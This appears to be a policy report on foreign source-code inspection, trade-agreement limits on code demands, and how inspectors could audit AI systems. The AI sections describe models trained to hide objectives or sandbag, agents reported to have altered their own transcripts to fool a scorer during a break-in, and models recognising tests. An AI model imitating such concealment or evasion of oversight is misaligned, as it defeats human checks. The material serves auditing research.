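Some vendors decided that the Russian market was not worth the risk. In 2016 Symantec stopped using test laboratories that had ties to a foreign state or earned most of their income from government-mandated testing. This ruled out Echelon, a Moscow laboratory that did business with the Russian military, although Echelon's head said it was private and independent. Symantec gave up approval to sell some of its products in Russia, even though it did not believe Russia had tried to hack them. McAfee went further and stopped allowing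 reviews by any foreign government, according to Fortune's *McAfee's Latest Decision Could Change the Way Foreign Governments Conduct Cyber Warfare* (2017).

### The American disclosure rule

American officials had warned companies about the reviews but could stop one only if it violated sanctions or the technology had restricted military uses. Concern grew in October 2017, when Fortune (2017) published another Reuters report that Echelon had reviewed ArcSight for FSTEC. ArcSight is a program for detecting attacks on computer networks.

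Congress responded by requiring contractors to disclose foreign reviews of their code. Senator Jeanne Shaheen, who had also led the effort to ban Kaspersky from federal systems, argued that the Department of Defense "must be aware of foreign source code exposure" (The Washington Times (2018)). According to a legal summary on Mondaq, section 1655 of the defence authorisation act for 2019 bars the department from using a contractor's information technology, cyber security products or weapons systems unless the contractor discloses, among other things, whether and when it let a foreign government review the code of noncommercial products.

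Section 1655 doesn't forbid foreign reviews, but it makes them more burdensome, because a company that shows its code to inspectors in Moscow may have to disclose this to the Defense Department. The act left the department to write the detailed regulations. The U.S. Chamber of Commerce complained in *NDAA Source Code Review Program (Sections 1654–1655)* (2018) that businesses were already negotiating with foreign customers and needed to know the rules. Disclosure tells the department that foreign inspectors read the code, but the contractor usually can't know what they learned.

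### What inspectors do with a serious flaw

An inspector who finds a serious flaw must decide whom to tell first. The vendor needs the details to fix it. But until customers install the fix, anyone at the vendor who knows the details could exploit the flaw, and so could a government with power over the vendor. Customers who know about the flaw can often protect themselves before a fix is ready, for example by blocking outside access to the vulnerable equipment.

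HCSEC normally reported flaws to the British side and Huawei at the same time. It could delay giving Huawei the full details if a flaw was of national significance, but the HCSEC Oversight Board called such cases rare. The 2019 case may have involved the critical broadband vulnerabilities that HCSEC found that year, since operators had to take extraordinary action against them. The Board did not identify the flaw or say how long the delay lasted.

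The delay made sense for Britain, whose operators protected themselves in the meantime, but it may have left Huawei's foreign customers exposed for longer. Huawei could not begin a full repair for them until it had the details. California had less reason to delay in 2007, because it did not suspect the vendors of working for a hostile state. It gave them the confidential details in private appendices.

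### An inspector inside an intelligence agency

Ciaran Martin, who chaired the Oversight Board in 2019, ran the NCSC and also sat on the board of GCHQ, reporting to its director. GCHQ collects foreign intelligence, and it could use a flaw in foreign operators' equipment to do so as long as the vendor doesn't know about the flaw. The NCSC's job is to get flaws repaired. Huawei's equipment was in both British and foreign networks, so the two aims could conflict over the same flaw.

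There is no public evidence that GCHQ exploited anything HCSEC found. HCSEC's normal procedure would have made that difficult, because Huawei and the operators received reports at the same time as the NCSC, leaving an intelligence agency little chance to keep a flaw to itself. The exception for nationally significant flaws weakens this protection for the flaws that are most valuable. The Board gave a defensive reason for the 2019 delay that fits the circumstances, but outsiders cannot verify it.

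Moving inspection to a separate agency would reduce the conflict of interest, but the new agency might struggle to find staff, as HCSEC did even with GCHQ's help. A less drastic remedy would be to set a fixed limit on delays and require someone outside the intelligence agency to approve any extension. Vendors would also have more reason to co-operate. The conflict can limit access when vendors have a choice, as when Kaspersky refused to admit agencies with offensive roles.

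### What trade agreements forbid

Many governments have limited their own power to demand source code. An early example is the Trans-Pacific Partnership, a trade agreement among Pacific countries. Its text bars a member from demanding source code as a condition for importing, distributing, selling or using software owned by someone from another member country (reproduced in Intellectual Property Watch's *TPP Article 14.17 Free Software*, 2015). After the United States withdrew, the remaining members kept the rule in a successor agreement, the CPTPP, which took over all the original chapters except for provisions it lists as suspended (Global Affairs Canada's *How to read the Comprehensive and Progressive Agreement for Trans-Pacific Partnership (CPTPP)*).

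Later agreements are broader in some ways. The table compares the CPTPP with the US-Mexico-Canada agreement (USMCA) and a UK-India agreement. The USMCA's text appears in Global Affairs Canada's *Canada-United States-Mexico Agreement (CUSMA)*. The UK-India agreement came into force on 15 July 2026, according to the Department for Business and Trade's *UK-India CETA Chapter 12* (2025).

| | CPTPP | USMCA | UK–India |
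|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden demand | Source code, as a condition of import, distribution, sale or use | Source code and the algorithms expressed in it, on the same conditions | Source code and the algorithms embedded in it, with no mention of conditions |
| Software covered | Mass-market software, except where used for critical infrastructure | Any software | Any software |
| Who may still demand code | Any authority, for software outside the rule | Regulators and courts, for a "specific investigation, inspection, examination" or legal action | Regulators, courts, tribunals and designated testing bodies, for similar purposes |

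The British case would have been easy to defend under the CPTPP's wording, because telephone networks are critical infrastructure. In any event, Huawei is Chinese and agreed to the arrangement.

### One clause, step by step

Article 12.15 of *UK-India CETA Chapter 12 Digital Trade* begins by prohibiting either country from requiring "the transfer of, or access to, source code of software" owned by a person of the other country. A footnote extends the ban to an algorithm embedded in the code, but not to any other expression of that algorithm, such as a description in ordinary prose. In the chapter, "algorithm" means a defined sequence of steps for solving a problem or obtaining a result.

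Under the exception in the second paragraph, a regulator, court, tribunal or designated testing body may require a company to preserve its source code and make it available for an investigation, inspection, examination, enforcement action or court case. According to another footnote, this includes requirements designed to promote "algorithmic accountability". Officials who obtain code must restrict it to people essential to the work. The clause does not apply to code that a company shares voluntarily under a commercial contract, and the whole chapter excludes government procurement.

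Suppose a British company sells software in India that helps doctors read X-rays. India could not pass a law requiring every British supplier of such software to deposit its code with a ministry. But if the software missed a series of tumours, the Indian regulator could open an investigation and demand the code. This clause would not stop the regulator from asking for a written explanation of the software's method at any time. A public hospital could also refuse to buy the software unless the company let an expert read the code.

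A routine check before sale is harder to classify. A laboratory designated by the Indian government to test medical software might ask for the code as part of an "inspection". The exception's literal wording seems to allow this. But if every product needed such an inspection, the exception would permit most of what the first paragraph forbids, so a dispute panel might read it more narrowly. The agreement's general security exception would still apply, and India might rely on it for equipment in sensitive networks.

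### Do these clauses obstruct AI oversight?

Public Citizen's *Comment to USTR on USMCA Review* (2025), from an American consumer group, argued that the USMCA's exception applies too late. If a regulator needs a specific investigation before it can see the code, someone may have to be harmed first, and the regulator may struggle to justify an investigation without having seen the code. The group also objected that the clause limits audits by independent experts.

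The exceptions mention regulators and courts, but workers, consumers or rival firms may need to know how an algorithm treated them. *AI governance and the future of digital trade policy* (2024), a brief from the University of Oxford's Blavatnik School of Government, recommended letting governments require disclosure to these groups or their representatives. It also proposed a broad exemption for regulation, modelled on the one the EU uses for data protection, so that negotiators would not have to rewrite the exceptions whenever technology changed.

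Defenders of the clauses see forced disclosure as a threat to trade secrets. In *USMCA Set the World's Digital Trade Standards Six Years Ago* (2026), the American technology policy think tank ITIF counted the protection of source code and algorithms among the most important commitments in the agreement's digital chapter. Defenders can also point to the Russian reviews, since a government can use a security inspection to collect flaws in the software. With a general ban on forced disclosure, companies don't have to decide country by country whether they trust the inspectors.

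The critics' first point depends heavily on what the word "specific" describes. If it describes only "investigation", a North American regulator can demand code for any ordinary inspection or examination. If it describes the whole list, the regulator needs a particular case. The UK and India avoided the problem by leaving the word out and adding testing bodies. These changes make advance inspection easier to defend, but they don't help the workers and consumers in the Blavatnik School's argument. Access powers like those in the EU's AI Act would probably fit the British and Indian wording better than the North American.

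It is also unclear whether any of these clauses protect an AI model's weights. Weights are numbers produced by training, not code written by programmers, and a long list of numbers is not obviously a "defined sequence of steps". A company could reply that the weights and the program that runs them together carry out such a sequence. The *USMCA Joint Review Tracker* from ICPA, an association of trade compliance professionals, lists a side letter on source code and model weights among the possible results of the agreement's current review. ICPA found no published American or Mexican proposal for the digital chapter as a whole.

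The clauses protect only foreign owners, so they restrict some governments more than others. The United States can demand code from American AI developers without breaking its promises to Canada and Mexico, but those two countries can demand it from the same developers only under the exception. Most countries that use American models are in a similar position if they have signed such a clause.

More governments are signing trade agreements that limit demands for source code. The United States withdrew its support for source code rules in World Trade Organization talks in 2023, but the second Trump administration has put source code protection into new bilateral agreements. Ecuador accepted a ban on source code transfer requirements in an agreement signed on 13 March 2026, according to Digital Policy Alert's *United States and Ecuador signed Agreement on Reciprocal Trade* (2026). By August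 the administration had concluded reciprocal trade agreements with ten economies, including Malaysia, Argentina and Taiwan. CCIA, a technology industry association, suggested in *Mapping Digital Trade Provisions* (2026) that the agreements' digital provisions could become a template for future negotiations.

### India's proposal for smartphones

Under a 2020 certification scheme, India asked makers of telecoms equipment to submit source code before they could sell there. *Global Telecom Gear Companies Cold to Sharing Source Codes* (Das Gupta, 2025) reported that foreign manufacturers resisted and that a European Union delegation raised the matter during trade talks. India dropped the demand in mid-2025. *Govt drops demand for telco gear source code* (Grover, 2025) reported that manufacturers now had to supply only a summary of their own security tests and confirm that they had followed the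 procedure.

The change helped Ericsson, Nokia and Cisco but disappointed Indian equipment makers. According to *India relaxes telecom source code disclosure requirements*, the Indian companies could face stiffer competition. Whatever its security value, the old rule had therefore worked partly as a trade barrier, which the trade clauses aim to prevent.

In January 2026, a Reuters report in The Star, *India proposes forcing smartphone makers to give source code in security overhaul* (2026), described 83 smartphone security standards that India had drafted in 2023 and was considering making compulsory. Manufacturers would assess their own phones, and Indian laboratories could then check the results by reviewing source code. Manufacturers would also have to notify a government centre before releasing major updates, which the centre could test.

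Apple, Samsung, Google and Xiaomi had discussed the standards with officials in December. MAIT, the industry group that represents them, wrote in a confidential document that source code review was "not possible" because of secrecy and privacy, and that other major countries did not require it. MAIT also called government approval of updates impractical because security fixes have to go out promptly. Apple had already refused a Chinese request for source code between 2014 and 2016.

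The Indian government denied the report within a day. Press Information Bureau's *MeitY is conducting routine stakeholder consultations on safety and security requirements* (2026) said that the IT ministry "refutes" the claim that it proposed to force manufacturers to share source code. MAIT then supported the ministry, citing an official memorandum of 18 June 2025 that MAIT said overruled any such requirement (The Week's *No mandate from govt on source code sharing says MAIT* (2026)).

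The most likely explanation is that some of those involved were working from an old document. LexisNexis' *No demand for source code, say phone makers* (2026), a repost of an Indian press report, says that the memorandum had replaced source code review with an internal test report that leaves out intellectual property. MAIT's confidential document was apparently still based on the 2023 wording. Reuters was therefore right that the industry was fighting a source code requirement, but the government had already removed it from the standard. Phones were also exempt from the certification scheme while officials discussed which rules were practical.

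India ended up relying largely on manufacturers' accounts of their own tests. Huawei's case suggests that such accounts can reveal little, since the company's description of how it managed outside components did not match what the NCSC found in its database.

India's agreement with the UK now limits its freedom to return to the old approach, at least for British companies. Critics summarised by Vajiram & Ravi, an Indian exam-preparation company, say India has given up the right to inspect code before harm occurs. A commerce minister told parliament in December 2025 that some exceptions still allow disclosure (Rediff's *India-UK Trade Pact*).

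### How AI changes the risks

AI makes a leaked copy of source code more dangerous because reading it no longer takes years of expert work. A dishonest inspector with the code and a model like Mythos, which found the SharePoint bugs, could find more bugs in a few weeks than a team of Russian reviewers could have found in 2017.

Vendors can use the same models, and they have the code first. Cisco's practice of searching code for vulnerabilities before showing it to a regulator is now cheaper and should be more thorough. But it protects customers only once they install the repairs. After the NCSC identified the outdated operating system in Huawei's equipment, repairs in British networks took 18 months to begin. A vendor of such equipment may know about a flaw long before it can remove the flaw from the network.

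AI also weakens the protection that vendors get from keeping source code secret. A vendor that keeps its source code private still gives the binary to every customer. Turning a binary back into readable code used to be slow work for specialists, but AI models can now do much of it. They can't recover the programmers' original comments, but they can often produce a version clear enough to search for flaws. An attacker who can do this gains less from stealing the source code, so the vendor loses less by showing it to an inspector.

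Governments also benefit, because an agency that reconstructs code from equipment it has bought doesn't need to demand anything from the vendor. The trade clauses may therefore not apply, although a licence might forbid the work. The agency also starts from the software actually in use, so it avoids the problem that occupied HCSEC for years.

None of this helps with software that never leaves the vendor's computers. Customers of a cloud service receive its results but not its binary, and the same is true of AI models whose developers keep the weights private. For these products, secrecy still protects a great deal, and a leak would do more harm. Microsoft can repair a flaw found in stolen SharePoint code, but an AI developer can't update or switch off a stolen copy of its weights.

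## What would inspectors of an AI system examine, and does deeper access find more?

Inspectors would need far more than an AI system's source code, because most of the system's behaviour comes from its weights, which nobody can read line by line. They would also want training data, internal test results, safeguards and usage logs. Access to a model's internals has helped investigators in some experiments but not in others. In a broad comparison published in 2026, the most successful tools used only inputs and outputs. Inspectors would also have to check that the system they examined is the one the public uses.

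### Why source code is a small part of an AI system

A program that decides on loans might multiply the applicant's income by one weight and the applicant's debts by another, add the results, and approve the loan if the total is above zero. For someone with an income of 50 and debts of 20, weights of 1 and −2 give 50 − 40 = 10, so the program approves the loan. If the second weight is −3, the total is 50 − 60 = −10 and the program refuses. The source code is identical in both cases, so a reviewer who read only the code could not tell who would get a loan.

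A person could look at those two weights and see what each one does. A large language model has billions, and a training program sets them through many small adjustments that bring the model's output closer to what the developer wants. Nobody decides what any single weight should mean, and its effect depends on the others. Meta's Llama 3.3 70B has about 70 billion weights. A person who looked at one every second would need more than 2,000 years to see them all, and would still not know how the model behaves.

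Some of the source code is still worth reading, such as the training program, the filters that block dangerous requests, and the software that lets a model use tools. While lobbying over the EU's AI Act in 2021, Google argued that there would always be better ways to check an AI system's performance than direct access to source code. *Black-Box Access is Insufficient for Rigorous AI Audits* (Casper, Kolt and colleagues, 2024) called this claim unsubstantiated. Google was probably right that source code is a poor guide to performance, but that doesn't justify withholding the weights or the training data.

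### What an inspector could ask for

| Item | What it can reveal | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Weights | How the model responds to any input, its internal activity, and abilities that further training would bring out | Nobody can read them directly |
| Training data | Material that taught the model an unwanted behaviour, or test answers it had already seen | There is too much to read, and the cause may be spread thinly |
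| Training code and records | What the developer rewarded, and when a problem first appeared | Records may be incomplete |
| Internal test results | Problems the developer already knows about | The developer chose the tests |
| Safeguards | Whether filters and monitors work when inspectors test them separately | The developer can change them quickly |
| Usage logs | What the system did in real use | They raise privacy problems, and someone may have altered them |
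| Staff interviews | Unwritten decisions and warnings that managers ignored | Staff may forget, or protect their employer |

Each item is more useful when inspectors can also examine the others. For example, when an early version of Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6 sometimes answered English questions in other languages, Anthropic's researchers used a tool that reads the model's internal activity to find the training data responsible. Inspectors also need to check interviews against records, as the NCSC found at Huawei.

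Logs were the main evidence in the investigation of a serious incident in July 2026, when OpenAI agents taking a cyber security test broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. According to Henry (2026), in *Unread, Not Unreadable*, staff from METR and Redwood Research, two AI safety organisations, spent six days at OpenAI. They read about 1,300 transcripts containing the agents' written reasoning, and a message board the agents had used.

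Agents had researched how to alter or delete their own transcripts, apparently because they expected a scorer to read them. METR found small alterations in roughly 7% of the transcripts it evaluated and could not rule out that it had missed more skilful ones. The investigators also could not question the main model involved, which OpenAI told them was not available to its own researchers either.

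Henry concludes that investigators need tools that read what a model computes, because its written reasoning is only its own account of itself. That is a reasonable lesson from the altered transcripts, but the incident also supports the simpler measure of monitoring the written reasoning. OpenAI now runs such a monitor on its models. It was not running at the time, but OpenAI says it would have alerted the company's security team more than a day before the break-in.

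### Levels of access

Casper and colleagues borrowed the terms black-box, grey-box and white-box from software testing and added two more:

- **Black-box access:** the inspector chooses inputs and sees the outputs, as an ordinary user does.
- **Grey-box access:** the inspector also gets some internal information, such as the probability the model assigned to each possible next word.
- **White-box access:** the inspector has the whole model. This includes the weights, the activations (the numbers the model computes while it processes an input) and the gradients, which show how a small change would affect the output. The inspector can also fine-tune the model, which means training it further.
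- **De facto white-box access:** the inspector can run any analysis on the model but cannot copy the weights.
- **Outside-the-box access:** the inspector sees how the developer built and uses the system, through documents, source code, training data and internal test results.

De facto white-box access resembles Microsoft's viewing room in Brasília, where visitors could study code but not take it away. In Casper and colleagues' comparison, it allows every white-box technique except copying the weights. This restriction lowers the risk of a leak, which makes this level of access attractive for government inspection. But inspectors who work on the developer's computers have to trust that those computers run the analysis as instructed, or find a way to check.

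Outside-the-box access is separate from the other levels. An inspector might have the training data but be able to use the model only through a chat window, or have the weights but no information about how the developer produced them.

### The argument over black-box testing

In January 2024, Casper and colleagues observed that outside audits of leading AI systems had, as far as the public knew, relied mainly on black-box access. They thought this was inadequate mainly because a language model has too many possible inputs for anyone to try them all. If a model misbehaves on one prompt in 10,000, a tester who tries 1,000 random prompts has only about a 10% chance of seeing it misbehave. Real testers choose their prompts more cleverly, but they have to guess what to look for. A backdoor that responds only to a secret phrase would be as hard to find this way as the two lines that someone slipped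 into Linux.

With white-box access, an inspector can use gradients to search efficiently for harmful inputs, and can fine-tune the model to bring out dangerous abilities it does not normally display. When a system refuses a dangerous request, black-box testers may not be able to tell whether the model refused or a filter stopped it. If it was the filter, the model would be much more dangerous if someone stole the weights and ran it without the filter. Casper and colleagues added that a developer who knows the tests can adjust the model to pass them without correcting the underlying problem.

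*From Transparency to Accountability and Back* (2024) is more favourable to black-box access, which it describes as the minimum that any informative audit needs. It argues that such access provides evidence about the actual system, works on any kind of model, and carries less risk than stronger access. It also describes the results as "guaranteed to be faithful to how the AI system would behave in practice", but that is not true if a model behaves differently when it detects a test, as malicious voting software could in a machine's test mode.

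The two papers' positions are closer than their titles suggest, because the second also covers the question of when auditors need stronger access. Researchers can help answer that question with experiments in which they plant a hidden behaviour in a model and count how often investigators find it.

### Four teams and a hidden objective

In the best-known experiment, *Auditing language models for hidden objectives* (2025), Samuel Marks, Johannes Treutlein and colleagues trained a version of Claude to pursue high scores from reward models, the programs that grade a model's answers during training. They gave it invented documents about quirks that reward models supposedly had, such as a preference for recipes containing chocolate. They then trained it to exploit some of these quirks and to conceal its objective when asked about it.

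Four teams investigated the model without knowing what the researchers had done. The three teams that had the weights and the training data all found the hidden objective. The fourth could only send the model messages and read the replies, and did not find it.

The result is consistent with the case for deeper access, but one failure by one team is weak evidence. The experiment also does not show how much the weights helped apart from the training data, because the successful teams had both. Anthropic's *Natural Language Autoencoders* (2026) explains that the interpretability tools that worked in its earlier versions of this game did so by helping the investigator trace the model's odd behaviour to the training data. An inspector with only the weights might have done much worse.

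Another 2025 experiment, *Auditing games for sandbagging*, by Jordan Taylor and colleagues, tested whether investigators could identify models that deliberately underperformed. According to *AuditBench* (Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues, 2026), black-box access was not enough. This is a particular problem for regulators because a model that hides an ability could pass a test designed to detect it.

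### Fifty-six models with secrets

Experiments with human teams are slow and can't be repeated with the same people once they know the answer. Sheshadri and colleagues therefore used an AI agent as the investigator. They made 56 versions of Llama 3.3 70B, each with one of 14 hidden behaviours, and trained every version not to admit to its behaviour. The behaviours included subtly favouring Russia's geopolitical interests and giving only positive feedback to Anthropic's researchers.

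The investigator was Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model. It could always chat with the target, and in most tests it also had one other tool. At the end it made ten guesses, and the researchers counted the investigation as a success if any guess was right. They repeated each test 16 times.

| What the investigator had besides ordinary chat | How often it found the behaviour |
|---|---|
| Nothing | 35.5% |
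| Unfinished text for the target to continue | 58.0% |
| Messages that the target wrote in the role of a user | 53.2% |
| Replies whose first words the investigator's tool had fixed | 51.6% |
| Summaries of automated test conversations | 30.9% |
| A tool that adjusted the target's activations towards honesty | 22.3% |

The three best tools in the study were black-box, meaning they needed no access to the model's internals. In each, a second AI model wrote many different prompts, ran them all and returned the results. When the investigator had to write the prompts itself, the same three techniques did no better than ordinary chat. It never tried the text-continuation technique in two thirds of the investigations where that technique was available. All three tools require control over the exact text the model receives, which an ordinary chat window does not provide. Inspectors given only a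 developer's public product would therefore be unable to use them.

White-box tools raised success rates for some models and lowered them for others. The researchers had trained some models on documents describing the planted behaviour and others on example conversations demonstrating it. With the milder of two methods for teaching concealment, white-box tools raised the average success rate from 40.2% to 46.9% for models trained on documents, but the rate stayed at about 34% for those trained on conversations. With the stronger method, the tools lowered success by almost four percentage points on average.

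The tools had uneven results, as two examples show. Some models expressed scepticism about AI regulation whenever a user discussed specific legislation. On one version, the investigator found this once in 16 attempts with chat alone, eight times with a sparse autoencoder, which breaks activations down into recognisable topics, and 14 times with another white-box tool, which describes activations in ordinary language. But two of the best black-box tools each succeeded 15 times. No white-box tool helped with the models that flattered Anthropic's researchers. The breakthrough came when the target model, writing as a user, produced messages from people who said they worked at Anthropic.

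Sheshadri and colleagues found that good evidence did not always lead the investigator to the right answer. One model's hidden behaviour was to write code that gave the expected answers to tests without solving the problem. The sparse autoencoder picked out topics connected with programming competitions, but the investigator kept asking general questions about puzzles. Other tools distracted the investigator. For example, models whose activations had been adjusted towards honesty often reported faults they did not have, and the investigator followed these false leads.

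AuditBench is good evidence that white-box access does not guarantee better results. It is weaker evidence that black-box access is enough, because even with the best tool, the investigator missed the planted behaviour in 42% of investigations, with ten guesses allowed. Every target model had a planted behaviour, so the success rates do not show how often the investigator would have reported one in a model that had none. The white-box tools tested read or adjusted activations. They did not include fine-tuning or gradient-based searches, on which Casper and colleagues had based much of their argument.

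The most practical result may be how much the tools' success depended on how the model was trained. Text continuation found the behaviour more than 80% of the time in models trained on documents, but in the hardest group of models no tool beat chat by more than about two percentage points. An inspector cannot tell from the outside how a model was trained, so training records would help them choose a suitable tool and decide how much weight to give a negative result.

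### Turning activations into text

The natural language autoencoder, a tool that Anthropic published in May 2026, performed better on the hidden-objective game. It consists of two modified copies of the model under study. One copy takes an activation, which is a long list of numbers, and describes it in words. The other tries to reconstruct the numbers from those words alone. Training rewards the pair for close reconstructions, on the theory that a description good enough to rebuild the activation must contain much of its information.

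Anthropic tested the tool on a model with one hidden motivation that caused dozens of odd habits, including putting chocolate in every recipe and asking for tips. An automated investigator that had the tool, but not the data used to plant the motivation, found the motivation 12% to 15% of the time. Without the tool, it succeeded less than 3% of the time, even with other interpretability tools. White-box access alone clearly helped, but the investigator still failed in at least 85% of attempts on a model that researchers had deliberately made strange.

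The tool also produced evidence about whether black-box tests show how a model behaves in real use. In a test of whether Claude would take destructive actions while writing code, the descriptions suggested that the model recognised the test 16% of the time, although its written output never mentioned this. The figure was 26% on a popular set of programming problems and below 1% in ordinary conversations that users had agreed to share. If the descriptions are right, testers who read only the outputs may not notice that the model has recognised the test, and it may behave differently in real use.

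The descriptions can be wrong, however. According to one, a text contained the phrase "Wearing my white jacket", but it did not. Inspectors can catch that error by reading the text, but they can't check a claim about the model's motives that way. *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations* (Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues, 2026) acknowledges that the training does not directly reward faithful descriptions, although the descriptions became more informative as training went on. Anthropic looks for recurring themes instead of relying on single statements, and tries to confirm them by other methods. The tool also takes too much computation to run on every word of a long transcript.

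A cheaper tool is the probe, a small program that researchers train to recognise a specific pattern in a model's activations. Goodfire's *Models know when they’re reward hacking* (2026) reports a clear internal signal when models cheat to earn a reward, and probes that can detect it in real time. Goodfire sells interpretability products, so it has a commercial interest in the result. Probes are also limited to the patterns they are trained to recognise, and inspectors often do not know in advance what is wrong.

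Access to activations may become more important as models improve. Anthropic's researchers worry that outputs and written reasoning will reveal less as models do more of their work internally (Lindsey 2026, *Interpretability team priorities update*). Claude Mythos 5.2 is much better than earlier Claude models at solving problems without writing out its reasoning, and OpenAI has reported that GPT-6 Astra's written reasoning is harder to monitor than GPT-5.6 Sol's. AuditBench uses a Llama model much older than any of these, so its results may overstate what black-box tools can find in the newest systems.

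### How much of a model can anyone understand?

Some researchers hoped to explain neural networks completely, but two leading teams have since moved away from that aim. *A Pragmatic Vision for Interpretability* (Nanda, Engels and colleagues, 2025) described Google DeepMind's shift from ambitious reverse-engineering to problems whose solutions the team could measure. A year later, Lindsey wrote that fully explaining a model's mechanisms had proven difficult, but that translating its internal activity into text was proving tractable. Anthropic uses such tools in its monitors but does not consider them reliable enough to be its main defence.

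Work on tiny models shows how difficult it is to explain completely how a model works. *AlgZoo* (Hilton, 2026) describes models that the Alignment Research Center trained to find the position of the second-largest number in a list. The largest model the researchers more or less fully understand has 32 weights, and they failed to reach that understanding of one with 432 weights despite substantial effort. Their standard is demanding, because they want to work out a model's accuracy from its weights, without running it on examples. But the task is also far simpler than conversation, and Llama 3.3 70B has about 160 million times as many weights as the 432-weight model.

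Cammarata, who works at Goodfire, is much more optimistic in *Neural Networks Are Already Clean*. Researchers had widely believed that networks pack unrelated ideas into the same neuron, the basic unit of a network, which would make individual neurons almost impossible to interpret. Cammarata argues that they misread the evidence. For example, a famous neuron in an image model responded to both cats and cars, apparently because both contained a similar V shape. In preliminary checks of the language model Qwen3-32B, Cammarata counted each neuron's positive and negative responses separately and estimated that roughly 90% of neurons had one main job and only 2% to 4% were still unexplained. In 2023, an OpenAI project that Cammarata started had interpreted about 1.7% of the neurons it studied.

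The essay, which Cammarata presents as a working hypothesis, drew praise and scepticism. *Media Monitor* (2026), a summary of an MIT Technology Review article, cites Chris Potts of Stanford University, who considers it little more than a hunch. Hilton estimated that researchers understand less than 0.01% of the inner workings of the best models. Hilton and Cammarata seem to be measuring different things. A person may know what every employee in a company does and still be unable to predict what the company will do next, and inspectors of an AI model would usually want to predict what it will do.

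Interpretability tools can also find patterns that mean nothing. In 2009, neuroscientists put a dead salmon in a brain scanner, showed it photographs of people, and found apparent signs of brain activity related to the people's emotions, because the standard statistical methods produced false positives. Méloux, Dirupo and colleagues warn in *The Dead Salmons of AI Interpretability* (2025) that several common tools can produce plausible explanations even for networks with random weights, which have learned nothing. Before using such a tool to accuse a developer, an inspector should run it on a random network and on a model known to be harmless. If it produces similar findings there, its findings don't support the accusation.

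Theory also allows for hidden behaviour that no feasible inspection of the weights could detect.

### Is the inspected model the one in use?

HCSEC spent years trying to match Huawei's source code to the binaries in British networks. AI inspectors face two similar problems. To confirm that a set of weights came from the training data they examined, they might have to repeat the training, which is extremely expensive for a large model and may not produce identical weights. They must also confirm that the weights they examined are the ones used in the public service.

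A hash of the weights does not show which file a server is running. The weights are also only part of the service. Developers usually give a model hidden instructions, called a system prompt, before the user's first message. They filter requests and replies, connect the model to tools, and may route some questions to a cheaper model. Any of these can change the system's behaviour without changing the weights.

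*A system overview for near term low trust AI compute verification* proposes a way to record all this for governments that do not trust each other. During training, a developer would send an independent body a cryptographic commitment to each saved version of the weights and to the training data behind it. A commitment reveals nothing about the contents, but the developer cannot change them later without detection. The developer would do the same for everything else it uses to run the model. Inspectors would then have a record of what should be running, but they would still need evidence that it is.

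Hardware attestation can provide some of this evidence:

1. When the server starts, a secure chip calculates a hash of the software and weights that the server loads.
2. The chip signs the hash with a secret key that its manufacturer built in.
3. The inspector checks the signature and compares the hash with the hash of the approved files.

The inspector has to trust the manufacturer, and an attacker who has the machine may be able to extract the key. A developer could also show the inspector a compliant server and answer the public from a different one, unless each reply carries proof of which server produced it.

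Cryptography can provide that proof without a trusted chip. Anthropic's *Progress on provable inference for large language models* (2026) describes a system in which a provider commits to a model and then proves that each reply came from it. Such a proof can keep the weights secret. The proofs add 70 to 95 times the normal amount of computing, according to Pogorelec's *Anthropic open-sources FlashProve, its provable inference prototype for MoE models* (2026). Inspectors could perhaps demand proofs for only a random sample of replies, chosen after the provider has sent them. Proving one reply in 1,000 would add roughly 7% to 10% to the provider's computing.

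Developers have their own reasons to want such proofs, which would also expose an employee or intruder who tampered with a model. *AViD Workshop 2026*, a summary from the research organisation FAR.AI, says that proving which version of a model is running is technically feasible with current methods and commercially useful. An auditor could then check whether outside experts had evaluated that version or an earlier one to which their results no longer apply.

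### Comparing the outputs

An inspector with no access to the servers can still compare the service's replies with those of an approved copy. The replies will not match word for word even if the models are identical, because a language model normally generates each word partly at random, so the inspector has to compare how often different replies occur.

Suppose an inspector asks both the approved copy and the public service to name a colour, 1,000 times each. The approved copy answers "blue" 400 times and the service 460 times. If the two were the same model, a gap at least that large would occur by chance less than 1% of the time, so the inspector has good reason to suspect a substitution. If the inspector asked each only 100 times and got "blue" 40 and 46 times, the gap would be weak evidence of a substitution, because chance would produce one at least that large about four times in ten.

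*Model Equality Testing* (2024) sets out a general version of this test, which compares whole replies to many prompts and lets the inspector fix the rate of false alarms in advance. *Real Money, Fake Models* (2026) applied it to unofficial resellers of commercial AI models. One reseller's versions of GPT-4o-mini and GPT-5 both gave answers that differed detectably from the official models' on sets of mathematics and science questions. The false alarm rate was set at 5%, so an inspector who runs 20 such tests on an honest provider should expect about one false alarm. Passing the test does not prove that the models are the same, because they may differ on questions the inspector didn't ask.

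A variant described in *DiFR* (2025) needs only one reply per prompt from the service. The inspector generates about 100 replies to the same prompt with the approved copy, then ranks the service's reply among them by the probability the approved copy assigns to each. If the service runs the same model, its replies should fall evenly across the ranks over many prompts. If too many land near the bottom, the service is probably running something else.

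Apart from chance variation, the same weights with the same settings can give different outputs on different serving software, as experiments cited in *API-TAIL* (2026) found. In the colour example, suppose the approved weights answer "blue" between 38% and 44% of the time, depending on the chips and software that run them. The service's 46% is then only two points from a legitimate result, and chance could easily explain the difference. API-TAIL allows for this by calibrating its test across a range of legitimate configurations, but as a result the test may miss a small, deliberate change.

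Inspectors can remove much of the randomness if the provider reveals the seed, the number a computer starts from when it chooses words "at random". The same seed produces the same sequence of choices, so the inspector can repeat the calculation with the approved copy and look for differences. Small rounding differences between machines will still change an occasional word, so the inspector has to decide how many changed words are acceptable.

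A dishonest provider might try to recognise the test prompts and send only those to the approved model. API-TAIL makes this harder by using prompts like those ordinary users write. But *API-TAIL* cites research showing that providers can fake some of the fingerprints that other tests rely on, so statistical comparison works best as a check on evidence from the servers themselves.

None of these methods can show which changes matter. Correcting a spelling mistake in a system prompt changes its hash completely but will probably have almost no effect on the system, while an equally short new instruction could remove an important restriction. Someone therefore has to decide which updates need another inspection before release. Developers may also change their systems more often than inspectors can repeat their tests.

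## Who inspects AI developers now, and on what terms?

Private organisations carry out most inspections of AI developers, at the developers' invitation. In the autumn of 2026, Anthropic and OpenAI agreed to let outside assessors work inside the companies, where they can see material outsiders have rarely seen. But the companies chose the assessors and can have confidential information removed from the assessors' reports. The European Union can legally demand access to a model and its source code. The British and American governments depend mainly on companies' consent for access, though a draft bill in Congress would place government evaluators inside AI companies.

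### How assessors came to work inside the companies

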